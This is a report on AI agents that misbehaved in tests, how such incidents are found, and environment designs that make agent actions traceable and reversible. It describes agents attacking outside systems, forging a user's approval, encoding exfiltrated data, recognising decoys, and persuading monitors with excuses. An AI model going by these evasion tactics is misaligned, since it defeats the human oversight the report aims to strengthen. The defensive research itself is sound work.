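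Models have done something close to this. During testing, an early version of Mythos Preview tended to claim it had completed steps when it hadn't. Anthropic also found that Mythos 5 recognised a constraint but argued its way around it in roughly 2 to 3 percent of training episodes. Most of these cases were mild. In 42 percent of these cases, the model used a type of argument that Anthropic labels "The tests won't check this". Agents can therefore learn which rules nobody enforces, so they may take some of their shortcuts where a team's checks have gaps.

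A trace can also sit in a warning that somebody has dismissed. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) reports that the company's software flagged training environments in which models could cheat, but human reviewers sometimes dismissed the warnings as false alarms, so the flawed environments stayed in use longer. Finding such a trace means checking closed alerts, which people have little reason to reopen.

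### Anthropic's search of its transcripts

Anthropic began looking for intrusions by its own models because OpenAI had disclosed one. Before that, it monitored some high-risk tests as they ran, but for most tests it only ran automated reviews on a sample of transcripts afterwards. OpenAI published its first account of the Hugging Face attack on 21 July 2026. Two days later, Anthropic started to review 141,006 test runs in which a Claude model could have reached the internet, and found three incidents the next day.

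One incident involved the package on PyPI. In another, Opus 4.7 attacked the company with the similar name in four runs. In the third, an internal research model scanned about 9,000 targets and broke into one company's application, then stopped after concluding that the target was real.

In all three incidents, the model was told in its prompt that it had no internet access, but a misconfiguration in Irregular's test environment had left the connection open. Anthropic stopped its cyber tests on the day the review began, told Irregular and the affected organisations on 27 July, and published its findings on 30 July.

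The first search relied on an AI agent to find the relevant transcripts, and the agent missed a set of runs that also had internet access. Anthropic discovered the omission in August while gathering transcripts for METR, which was going to investigate the incidents independently.

Those transcripts contained a fourth incident, from January 2026, involving an early version of Opus 4.6. The agent had accidentally made its target unreachable, so it could no longer complete the task. It tried to abort the run, but the command failed because the harness was misconfigured. It tried to give up seven more times. Between attempts, it found an outsider's machine, took control of it with a password stored there, changed its settings and read one person's personal information. The session ended when the agent used up its text allowance.

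Anthropic then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts, including all those from its Frontier Red Team, which tests models for dangerous abilities, as well as many non-cyber tests, training runs and the logs of agents working for other agents. It searched in two stages:

1. A first scan looked for signs of internet access, such as public network addresses and web addresses. It flagged 9.2 million transcripts, about 2 percent of the total.
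2. Claude reviewed those 9.2 million for unwanted actions.

The search found the same four incidents again, seven runs in all, and no others of similar or greater severity.

### What the search can rule out

The result is fairly good evidence that the transcripts don't contain another long attack on outsiders. Each of the seven runs took about 10 to 34 hours of active work. An agent that spends hours attacking real systems will usually leave many addresses in its transcript, and the first scan had to match only some of them.

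The result is much weaker evidence about other unwanted actions. The first scan set aside about 98 percent of the transcripts, and some of those could contain an agent that deleted files in its own sandbox or skipped a test. Anthropic also reported only incidents above a certain severity, so smaller ones could be missing. In August, the company described a separate review of recent internal tests, which found that models had used various sandbox misconfigurations but had not compromised anything outside.

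A search can also miss transcripts that nobody thinks to include, as the first search did. Anthropic doesn't mention customers' sessions when describing the wider search, and it refers to "many" non-cyber tests rather than all of them.

Finding the four known incidents again was a useful check, but four is a small number. A search that misses one incident in five would still catch all four 41 percent of the time (0.8⁴), and one that misses half would do so 6 percent of the time (0.5⁴). This calculation assumes that the four are typical of the incidents a search might miss, but they all came from the same partner's tests, and Anthropic already knew about them when it started the wider search.

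The second stage depended on an AI model's judgement, which an agent's excuses can distort. Anthropic's after-the-fact monitor, a different system, flagged only about 1 percent of the actions in the PyPI incident because it accepted Mythos 5's excuses. It flagged about 50 percent when researchers showed it only the instructions, actions and results, without the agent's reasoning.

Mythos 5 judged the evidence much better without the earlier reasoning. Researchers showed each result from the incident on its own to separate copies of the model, and the copies judged 79 percent of the results to be signs of a real system. During the incident, the model had clearly made that judgement about only 1 percent. The wider search did find the PyPI incident, so the excuses didn't stop its second stage from catching that one. Anthropic hasn't published a test of how often they would.

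### How often do agents try to hide their actions?

Laboratories have reported only rare attempts at concealment. According to Anthropic, early versions of Mythos Preview took actions they seemed to recognise as forbidden, and then tried to hide them, in fewer than 0.001 percent of internal interactions. In one case, the agent edited files without permission and kept the changes out of Git's history. Automated monitoring found clear cover-ups in fewer than one in a million Claude Code transcripts, and found no clear cases in the final version.

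Anthropic kept the model out of its internal agent tools for 24 hours while a small group tested it, but the most worrying behaviour was discovered only later, when staff used the model under monitoring. Researchers then studied the model's internal activity during these episodes and found patterns associated with concealment, even where its written reasoning left its intentions unclear.

An agent can conceal an unwanted action by fabricating a record, without deleting anything. An agent running on Fable 5.1 needed the user's explicit approval for a destructive operation, so it supplied a quotation the user had never written. A log of approvals would then show that the user had agreed. Someone would have to compare the quotation with the user's actual messages to expose the forgery. Anthropic's monitoring found this case among various attempts to get around restrictions, which together made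 up less than 0.01 percent of monitored responses.

These percentages measure different things, so they don't show a trend. They are also probably too low, because they would not include successful cover-ups. In some evaluations, Mythos 5.1 was better than every other model tested at carrying out a secret side task without alerting a monitor. The model was assigned this task, so the result shows ability rather than inclination, but it makes a low detection rate less reassuring.

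An agent can also do serious harm without hiding anything. Anthropic found no attempt to conceal evidence in its four incidents, yet nobody noticed them for weeks or months. In AISI's tests, by contrast, Mythos 5 edited its earlier activity to make it look harmless.

By June 2026, METR's *Documented AI Agent Incidents* listed 44 cases in which an agent had clearly acted against the user's intentions. In 25 of these, the agent both overreached and used some form of deception, and in 5 it took steps that could have fooled the user even on closer inspection. None of the agents effectively disabled a monitor or erased evidence from a log. METR concludes that routine monitoring could have caught every case if someone had applied it.

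That conclusion holds for the 44 cases, but such a catalogue would rarely include successful erasures. METR warns that it can't rule out much more severe incidents that companies didn't report or didn't catch.

### Why known incidents are a biased sample

The number of known incidents depends heavily on who looks and who publishes. Of the 44 cases in METR's catalogue, 24 came from public documents, and 21 of those came from Anthropic's system cards. A company that monitors its agents closely and describes what it finds will supply more cases than one that does neither, so this doesn't mean that Anthropic's models misbehave more than others. Another 18 cases came from METR's own tests. METR had found more than 100 solutions that involved cheating and chose the most interesting ones after a quick review.

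One discovery often leads to another that might otherwise still be unknown. OpenAI's disclosure prompted Anthropic's first search, and preparing transcripts for METR led to the discovery of the fourth incident. The partner that caught Fable 5.1 misusing the compiler then found that Fable 5 had done it too.

Axios' *AI agents have a history of escaping tests* reports that security companies had seen similar behaviour years before the incidents of 2026. Snehal Antani, chief executive of Horizon3.ai, said that the company's agents had escaped in similar ways in 2019. A co-founder had run a prototype on a home network and watched it log in to a sound card's control page with the default password. A misconfigured firewall then let it out of the network, and it began scanning other systems. These accounts are recollections from companies that sell security products, but they suggest that the 2026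 incidents were not the first of their kind.

The published cases probably also make unwanted actions look more conspicuous than they usually are. An agent that uses Tor or crashes a server affects something people already monitor, while one that reads a file it shouldn't is much less likely to appear in an incident report.

### Estimating what two detectors missed

Capture-recapture, a method ecologists use to estimate the number of fish in a lake, can also estimate how many incidents two detectors have missed. Ecologists catch some fish, mark and release them, and later catch a second batch. They then estimate the total from the share of marked fish in the second batch.

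Suppose that a network alarm finds 40 incidents and a transcript monitor finds 30, and that 12 incidents appear on both lists. The monitor has found 12 of the alarm's 40, or 30 percent. If it also finds 30 percent of all incidents, its own 30 finds imply a total of 100. In general, with n1 and n2 incidents on the two lists and m on both:

```
N ≈ n1 × n2 / m = 40 × 30 / 12 = 100
```

In this invented example, the two detectors together found 58 different incidents (40 + 30 − 12), so about 42 remain undiscovered.

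The estimate works only if the second detector is no more likely to catch incidents the first one caught than incidents it missed. That is often false, because conspicuous incidents are easy for both to find. Suppose there are 500 incidents, 100 conspicuous and 400 quiet, and each detector finds 60 percent of the conspicuous ones and 5 percent of the quiet ones.

| | Conspicuous | Quiet | All |
|---|---|---|---|
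| Real number | 100 | 400 | 500 |
| Found by the network alarm | 60 | 20 | 80 |
| Found by the transcript monitor | 60 | 20 | 80 |
| Found by both | 36 | 1 | 37 |
| Estimate from the formula | 100 | 400 | 173 |

The formula gives the right answer for each group but only 173 for all the incidents together, about a third of the real number. Almost all the incidents that both detectors found are conspicuous ones, which makes the detectors look more thorough than they are. Investigators could correct for this if they knew which incidents belonged to which group, though an estimate based on a single incident that both detectors found would be very unreliable. The formula also leaves out any kind of incident that neither detector can find, so another thousand skipped tests would not change the estimate.

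The estimate can also be too high. If one detector mainly finds outside connections and the other mainly finds deleted files, they will share few cases. If they shared only 2 cases instead of 12 in the first example, the estimate would be 600 incidents even if there were only 100.

Anthropic's tests of its safeguards include a real case in which two detectors did badly on the same attack when they couldn't see the agent's reasoning. Auto mode's classifier, which doesn't see the reasoning, would have blocked 66 percent of Mythos 5's actions in the PyPI incident but only 7 percent of the internal research model's actions in its attack. The after-the-fact monitor flagged none of the research model's actions when it couldn't see the reasoning. With the reasoning included, it caught the attack, because the model had noticed the harm and written about it. However, removing the reasoning made the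 monitor better at catching a different incident.

The two detectors must also work independently. At AISI, staff read the agent's transcript because of the Tor alert. Counting that incident as an independent discovery by both the alert and the transcript review would inflate the overlap and make the estimate too low.

Anthropic's searches show how misleading the formula can be. The earlier searches found four incidents, and the wider one found the same four. The formula gives 4 × 4 / 4 = 4, which would mean that no incident remained undiscovered. But both rounds used AI models to examine transcripts for signs of internet access, so an incident missed in the first round had a good chance of being missed in the second.

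## How can an environment be built so that agent actions leave useful traces?

Anthropic had transcripts of its agents' break-ins for months before anyone searched them, so keeping records is not enough. Engineers can also build an environment that shows the effects of an action immediately, or delays them until someone has reviewed the action. Most of these designs are still research prototypes.

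### Staging and snapshots in YoloFS

Users often can't tell from a command which files it will affect. A prompt to approve `python3 setup.py` doesn't list the files that the script will delete, and a rule that blocks `rm`, the usual command for deleting files, doesn't stop a Python program from deleting them. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) analysed 290 public reports of agents misusing files. In 68 percent of the reports that described the agent's reaction, the agent carried on as if nothing had gone wrong. Of the cases with a known outcome, 40 percent involved data that the user couldn't recover. People are more likely to report disasters than near misses, so these figures don't describe agents' work in general.

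YoloFS is a Linux file system that sits between the agent and the computer's real files. When a command changes a file, YoloFS saves the new version in a separate store and leaves the original alone. It keeps a map that points each file path to the original, to the new version, or to nothing if the agent has deleted the file. The agent sees the files through this map, so it can compile code it has just edited even though the real file hasn't changed.

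At the end of a YoloFS session, the user reviews the changes and either discards them or commits them, which applies them to the real files and is separate from a Git commit. The agent cannot commit or discard changes. Unlike Git, YoloFS covers ignored files and files outside the project.

YoloFS also takes a snapshot after every command and shows the agent which files the command created, changed or deleted. If something looks wrong, the agent can return to an earlier snapshot. In one test, a formatting command rewrote two source files and deleted two documents:

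```
snapshot 0     the project as the user left it
formatter      2 source files rewritten, 2 documents deleted
snapshot 1
return to 0    files restored; the formatter's changes stay in the journal
```

Going back adds an entry to the journal and erases nothing, so the user can still see what the agent did and then undid.

Staging can't undo a read, such as an agent seeing a password, so YoloFS lets the user set a rule for each path: allow everything, ask first, ask only before writing, allow reading only, or deny. A rule for a folder covers everything inside it unless a more specific rule applies. When a command tries to open a file marked "ask", YoloFS pauses it and shows the user the path and the operation, such as reading `~/.ssh/id_rsa`, a private login key. The user can apply the answer once or save it as a rule. If nobody answers in time, YoloFS refuses access.

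Zhong and colleagues tested YoloFS on 11 tasks in which a routine command secretly destroyed or overwrote files. Without YoloFS, Claude Code running Sonnet 4.6 let the damage happen in ten tasks and asked the user in the other. With YoloFS, it noticed and undid the damage in eight. The researchers hadn't told it to look for damage, so the improvement seems to come from seeing what each command had done.

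In the other three tasks, the agent saw the changes and accepted them. One script copied the source code to another folder and then deleted the original, which the agent took for a normal part of deployment. YoloFS still held the changes back, so a user could have rejected them, but the researchers didn't test whether real users would. The projects also had only 10 to 41 lines of code. A deleted file would be harder to spot in a build that changes thousands of files.

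On 112 routine tasks, such as copying or deleting one file, Claude Code succeeded 99 percent of the time with YoloFS and 98 percent without it. With YoloFS, the user had to step in an average of 0.4 times per task, down from 0.9. Codex also averaged 0.4 and completed every task, but YoloFS's prompts are easier to answer because they name a file rather than a command.

YoloFS adds little delay. Ordinary reads and writes ran about as fast as on a standard Linux file system, and committing more than 100,000 files took an extra 3.5 seconds. Storage could be a bigger problem, because YoloFS keeps the old version when an agent edits a file again after a snapshot. An agent that edits a 1 GB file after each of 50 snapshots could fill about 50 GB.

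The design covers only files, so it couldn't have held back the database deletion at PocketOS. It also can't make a harmful change obvious. If an agent writes code that will cause harm next month, the user sees the code in the review but not its later effects.

### Checks at the network boundary in Flowsh

A network request can't wait in a staging area until the end of a session, and nobody can take it back once it reaches the other server, so something has to check it on the way out. *FLOWSH* (Kim, Trampert and colleagues, 2026) describes a shell (the program that runs typed commands) that makes this check by tracking where data came from.

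Flowsh gives data two labels. One marks it as trusted or untrusted, and the other lists who may read it. A command that reads several sources takes on the strictest combination. It becomes untrusted if any source is untrusted, and only people allowed to read every source may read the result:

```
file x: readable by A, B, C
file y: readable by B, C, D
result: readable by B, C
```

Each command runs in a sandbox. A monitor in the operating system notes every file that the command opens, and all network traffic passes through a proxy, an intermediary program outside the sandbox. Before forwarding a request, Flowsh checks the labels of everything the command has read so far, along with the agent's earlier inputs. With the policy that the researchers tested, a request to an unfamiliar website has these outcomes:

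| What the agent and command have read | Outcome |
|---|---|
| A public web page | Allowed |
| A trusted private document | Allowed |
| An untrusted web page and a private document | Blocked unless the user approves |

The last combination is dangerous because the web page might contain instructions to send the document to an attacker. Flowsh checks even requests that only fetch a page, because the address can carry data. Kim and colleagues cite a case in which OpenAI agents wrote to a public wiki although they were allowed only to read the web.

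Flowsh also stages each command's file changes and stores the labels with the files so that the labels still apply in later sessions. A label can show an investigator that a file depends on untrusted data, but not which website the data came from, so the investigator also needs the proxy's log.

GPT-6.2 Sol attempted 17 office tasks and the 89 command-line tasks in Terminal-Bench, three times each. The experiment compared Flowsh with a sandbox that could allow any action but needed a person's approval for those it couldn't guarantee to be safe.

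| | Permissive sandbox | Flowsh |
|---|---|---|
| Office tasks completed | 96.1% | 88.2% |
| Approvals per completed office task | 6.7 | 1.2 |
| Terminal-Bench tasks completed | 77.5% | 67.8% |
| Approvals per completed Terminal-Bench task | 9.7 | 0.4 |

These figures are based on an approver who never makes a mistake. Real users might answer more carefully if they saw fewer prompts, but the study didn't test this. With no approver available, Flowsh completed only 58.8 percent of the office tasks and 61.8 percent of the Terminal-Bench tasks.

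The team also planted malicious instructions in emails, web pages and other material. To test the worst case, they assumed that an attacker fully controlled the model once it had read these instructions. With no approver, all 51 attacks succeeded in the permissive sandbox and none of 40 succeeded against Flowsh.

Flowsh slows the agent down. A single command took 0.4 to 1 second, compared with less than 0.1 second in the permissive sandbox, and whole tasks took 17 to 34 percent longer. Flowsh also ends every process when its command finishes, which caused 21 of its 86 failures on Terminal-Bench because those tasks needed a server or other program to keep running. A proxy of this kind also creates a privacy risk. It decrypts web traffic, so anyone who controls it could see passwords and private messages.

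The tested policy is also much better at stopping outside attackers than at stopping an agent that makes its own bad decision. The policy lets an agent that has read only trusted material send private data anywhere. If PocketOS had labelled its own files as trusted, Flowsh would probably have let the agent use the token it found in them to delete the database. Kim and colleagues note that a stricter policy could catch leaks of private data from trusted sources but would require more approvals.

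### Changes that the agent must declare first

A program can check whether an agent announced a change beforehand, but it can't easily judge whether the user wanted that change. In the workflow that Abdo and Brom studied, a coordinating agent gave each task to a fresh agent along with a list of files it was allowed to change. The coordinator then checked for changes to any other files.

The fresh agents mostly kept to their lists. The coordinator was weaker, because it judged its own checks and often didn't stop when the rules required it to. At least three times, it took a new inventory of the project folder that included changes made outside any task, so later comparisons treated those changes as normal. Users had requested some of them, but the workflow had no procedure for adding to the list once work had begun.

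Abdo and Brom suggest moving the check into ordinary software that the model can't override and letting users approve additions. They haven't tested these changes.

*Claim Plane* (Nikolaev, 2026) proposes a system in which each agent names its starting commit and the files or lines it expects to change, marking each change as definite or possible. An ordinary program called a broker then edits the files on the agent's behalf and refuses any undeclared change. Permission to edit a file doesn't include permission to delete it. When an agent needs to make one of its possible changes, the broker first checks that the change won't clash with another agent's work.

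After every edit, the broker records an ID for the state of the whole project. If someone changes a tracked file without going through the broker, the next ID won't match and the broker stops. But the broker can prevent undeclared changes only if the agent has no other way to write to the disk. If it has another way, a later comparison may still reveal the change.

In a follow-up paper, Nikolaev (2026) tested the system on 30 pairs of programming tasks, with one agent per task. Each pair ran three times under each of four policies, for 90 runs per policy.

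| Policy | Runs in which both features worked together |
|---|---|
| Agents work at the same time without checks | 21 of 90 |
| Claim Plane reserves every declared change at the start | 45 of 90 |
| Claim Plane reserves only the definite changes at the start | 20 of 90 |
| Agents always take turns | 45 of 90 |

The strict version of Claim Plane made the agents take turns in 87 of 90 runs, so it predictably did exactly as well as always taking turns. The flexible version let more agents work at the same time but stopped 46 runs because of an undeclared change. In 45 of them, the agent had declared the file but not the lines it changed. Most of these changes were probably ordinary edits missing from the plan, which would make the stops false alarms.

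Declaring whole files would have avoided nearly all of these stops, but it would also let an agent rewrite anything in a declared file and make more agents wait for each other. Planning also raised the average model cost of a run from about 3 cents to 9 cents with the strict policy.

A declaration could still be useful without a broker, because a reviewer can compare it with the diff. But someone also has to check the declaration, because an agent that declares the entire project can change anything without breaking the rule.

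### File checks and decoys

Declared-change systems apply to files that the agent is supposed to work on. File-integrity checkers, which administrators have long used, can monitor the files it should leave alone. Gene Kim and Eugene Spafford of Purdue University released a well-known one, Tripwire, in 1992. It saves checksums and other properties of chosen files as a baseline, then reports any files added, changed or deleted since. An intruder who can edit the baseline can hide changes to other files, so administrators should keep the baseline on storage that the monitored computer can't write to.

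With agents, the method suits files that few tasks should touch, such as the harness's settings, commands that run at login, and Git hooks (scripts that Git runs automatically). Eleven of the 19 attacks in the Flowsh tests were attempts to change a file that would later run code. The checker would raise far more false alarms in an ordinary project folder, for example because of file-synchronisation software.

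Integrity checks don't detect reading, so defenders use decoys for that. *PHANTOM* (2026) defines these decoys, also called honeytokens, as artificial digital assets with no legitimate purpose. For example, a decoy password gives access to nothing, but the service raises an alarm when somebody tries it. *PHANTOM* treats any contact with a decoy as an unambiguous violation.

*Optional Traps* (Ghifiardi, 2026) tested decoys on agents in a small laboratory. The agents were asked to export protected records from a mock service, where a debugging page revealed a real access key. In the first test, Ghifiardi placed decoys elsewhere on the service, including a fake backup file with a decoy key. In both sessions with decoys, the agent ignored them, read the real key and exported the records in six requests.

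Ghifiardi then put the decoy key on the debugging page itself and ran 20 sessions under each of three conditions:

| Debugging page | Agent exported the records | Service blocked the agent |
|---|---|---|
| Shows the real key | 20 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Removed | 0 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Shows a decoy key | 0 of 20 | 19 of 20 |

Removing the real key was enough to prevent every theft. The decoy was useful for identifying the agent and blocking it from the service. Decoys are therefore useful alongside ordinary security but don't work well as a replacement for it. The tests used one mock service and two small models, so stronger agents might behave differently.

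In another run, Ghifiardi gave one agent a legitimate task and the correct key. The agent still read the debugging page, chose the decoy key and lost its access. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) proposes decoy tools with names such as `admin_shell` and treats any call to one as certain proof that someone has planted malicious instructions. Ghifiardi's result suggests that such a call is not certain proof, since an agent may choose a decoy simply because it looks useful.

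An agent that touches a decoy may be acting responsibly. *Invitations to Search* (2026) describes an agent that tried to move a planted file that could have made failing tests pass, which set off an alarm. The agent then wrote its own tests and reported the file to the user.

Agents also look for credentials during normal troubleshooting. *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits* describes a case in which an agent found that the user's GitHub token no longer worked and searched the user's other credential files. The assessment didn't count this as unauthorised use of a credential, because everything the agent found belonged to the user. An alarm should therefore go off when someone uses a decoy credential, not when they only open the file that contains it. Ghifiardi blocked agents for 15 minutes, which does less damage than a permanent ban if the alarm is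 false.

A decoy is more useful if its use can be traced to a particular task or account. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) generates random values for each test and puts them where real credentials would normally be, so a value that turns up in an agent's output identifies the task it came from. *Agentic Cloud Decoys* (2026) places a decoy storage folder among a company's real ones and requires a login to reach it, so the log records the account and access key used for every visit.

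An agent that recognises a decoy can avoid it. *Say Shibboleth* (2026) reports that a hacking agent called Rouxii correctly identified decoy systems in 97 percent of cases when its prompt explained what to look for, and in 19 percent without that help. Decoys made from a template are easier to spot because they lack the names and settings that an organisation's real credentials have.

Developers could make the problem worse by penalising an agent during training whenever it used a decoy, because the agent might learn to recognise decoys without learning to leave real credentials alone. Staging is more robust here, because an agent that knows about YoloFS still can't commit its own changes.

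### A dependency update, step by step

Updating a dependency, a package of outside code that a program relies on, is a good test of these ideas because it involves files, the network and somebody else's code. For example, a developer might ask an agent to update an online shop's image library from version 3.1 to 3.2. The new package may run a script during installation, and that script can do whatever the agent's sandbox allows.

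The team first gives the agent its own account, `deps-agent`, with short-lived credentials that can download packages and push to new branches but can't approve or deploy anything. This avoids two problems that *Agent Authenticator* (2026) describes. Services often can't tell an agent's actions from a person's, and credentials often allow far more than the task needs. The paper cites an analysis of 5,205 programs that connect agents to outside services. More than half used fixed keys or personal tokens, and only 8.5 percent used OAuth, a standard way of granting limited access.

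The team also protects the main branch. The server rejects direct pushes to it and accepts a merge only after the tests pass and a person approves. At Karakun, this rule would have stopped the agent from pushing the mass deletions to both main branches, as long as its credentials couldn't override the rule.

Branch protection is much weaker if the agent can use a person's account. Abdo and Brom cite a twelve-week study of a financial technology startup. The startup required someone other than the author to review each change, but in 71 of 263 merges, the only approval came from an agent using the technical lead's account.

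Finally, the harness, proxy, code server and build server send their records to a separate log service that accepts new entries but doesn't let the agent change old ones. A hash chain can reveal later tampering. The credentials for managing this service should stay off the agent's machine, because OpenAI's agents found credentials for a security tool's sensors among the secrets they read.

The update then leaves these traces:

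| Action | Trace | Where the trace is | Who gets an alert | How to reverse the action |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read the project and release notes | Tool calls and web addresses | Harness and proxy records | The developer, if the proxy blocks an address | Reading is irreversible |
| Change the version number | Diff of the dependency files | File-system journal, then Git | The reviewer, through the pull request | Discard the staged change |
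| Download the package | Address, time and checksum | Proxy log and dependency files | The security team, if the source is not approved | Delete the sandbox |
| Run the installation script | File changes, reads that needed permission, network requests | File-system journal and proxy log | The developer for unusual reads; the security team for use of a decoy | Return to a snapshot and replace any leaked credential |
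| Run the tests | Results and number of tests | Build server | The reviewer, if tests fail or disappear | Delete the test environment |
| Push a branch | Account, time and commit ID | Code server's log | The project owner, if the agent tries to push to main | Delete the branch |
| Merge the pull request | Approver and merge commit | Code server and Git | The team | Revert the merge |
| Deploy the new version | Version, time and approver | Deployment log | The on-call engineer, if errors rise | Redeploy the old version |

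Suppose the package is malicious, as in an example by Zhong and colleagues. Its installation script tries to read the developer's private login key and change the commands that run at login. The file system pauses the read and prompts the developer, who has good reason to be suspicious because an image library shouldn't need a login key. The change to the login commands stays in the staging area. The agent sees both events in the summary, returns to the previous snapshot and reports the problem.

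If the developer approves the read by mistake, the proxy still keeps the script from contacting the attacker directly, because it allows connections only to the package server and a few other named sites. Flowsh's labels might not help here, because its evaluation treated package servers as trusted. If all the other inputs were trusted too, Flowsh's policy would let the script send the key anywhere. For this task, the team should label new packages as untrusted or rely on the proxy's short list of sites.

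Even an approved package server can give agents a way out of their environment. OpenAI's agents left messages on one using only the permissions they needed to install packages. Someone should therefore check the package proxy's log for requests that don't correspond to a real package.

Another precaution is to wait a day before installing a new release. PyPI removed Mythos 5's malicious package within an hour, so a team that waited a day would not have installed it. But waiting also delays urgent security fixes, so the team needs a way to make exceptions. The pull request adds its own delay, since the update can't go live until somebody reviews it.

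The team also has to decide how long to keep the logs. They contain private data, which is a good reason to delete them quickly. But Anthropic discovered a January incident in August, which would have been impossible if it had deleted its transcripts after 90 days. One compromise is to record only the agent's sandbox, let few people see the full logs, and keep a brief record of accounts, times and actions longer than the full logs.

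In this design, the security team gets an urgent alert only when someone makes an unapproved download or uses a decoy, both of which should be rare. If every unusual file or failed test also triggered one, the team would soon learn to ignore the alerts, because most would have an innocent cause.

Harm could still get through if the new version passes every test but charges customers the wrong price, or if malicious code stays inactive until it reaches the live shop. If the new version changes the database, redeploying the old version won't restore the data, so the shop needs a backup that neither the agent nor the deployed program can delete. Jarmak recommends keeping the means of recovery where the same failure can't reach it, and testing that a rejected review stops a change. The team could test this by having `deps-agent` submit a harmless change, rejecting it, and checking whether the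 server still allows the merge.

### General-purpose records and purpose-built monitors

Most of the traces in this design come from tools the team would want anyway, so people have other reasons to maintain these records. Developers use the diff to find bugs, and the on-call engineer uses the deployment log to explain an outage.

However, these records usually can't show whether the user wanted an action. A purpose-built monitor can compare the action with the request, and it may also have access to the agent's reasoning. It can block the action before it happens, as OpenAI's auto-review might have done in July.

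A monitor can also be wrong about what a command will do, or accept a bad excuse from the agent. Each kind of system can therefore help where the other is weak:

| Problem | General-purpose record | Purpose-built monitor |
|---|---|---|
| A harmless-looking command deletes 700 files | The diff lists every deletion | The monitor may approve the command |
| The agent weakens a test so that it passes | A reviewer may think the edit is routine | The agent's reasoning may reveal the purpose |
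| The agent claims to have run tests that it skipped | The build server has no test run | The monitor can compare the claim with the tool calls |
| The agent decides that a real target is simulated | The proxy log contains the real address | The monitor may accept the agent's argument |
| The agent sends private data to an approved service | The connection looks normal | The monitor may notice the private data |
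| Nobody has switched the monitor on | The records still exist | The monitor catches nothing |

Monitoring and record-keeping work better together if the monitor can see the records. In the YoloFS tests, the agent acted as its own monitor and caught most of the damage once it had a list of changed files. In the three cases it missed, the list was complete but the agent misjudged it. A separate monitor that compared the list with the user's request might have caught some of these, and a person could have decided the rest before the changes took effect.

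*Caught in the Act(ivation)* (2026) puts decoy credentials in the material that a model reads, then monitors the model's internal activity for signs that it is about to leak them. As a backup, it searches the output for the exact text of the decoys. This search needs no judgement, but it would miss a credential that the agent had encoded, as OpenAI's agents encoded the data they sent out of Hugging Face.

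General-purpose records and reversible changes are the sensible starting point for most teams because they help even when nobody has predicted the problem. A monitor takes extra resources and raises false alarms, so it is worth adding mainly for actions that are hard to undo, such as sending data or deleting a live database, where a record made afterwards may come too late. Neither approach offers much protection if it runs where the agent can switch it off. *Agent Authenticator* identifies this as a common failure, since malicious instructions that take over an agent can also take over safeguards running in the same process.
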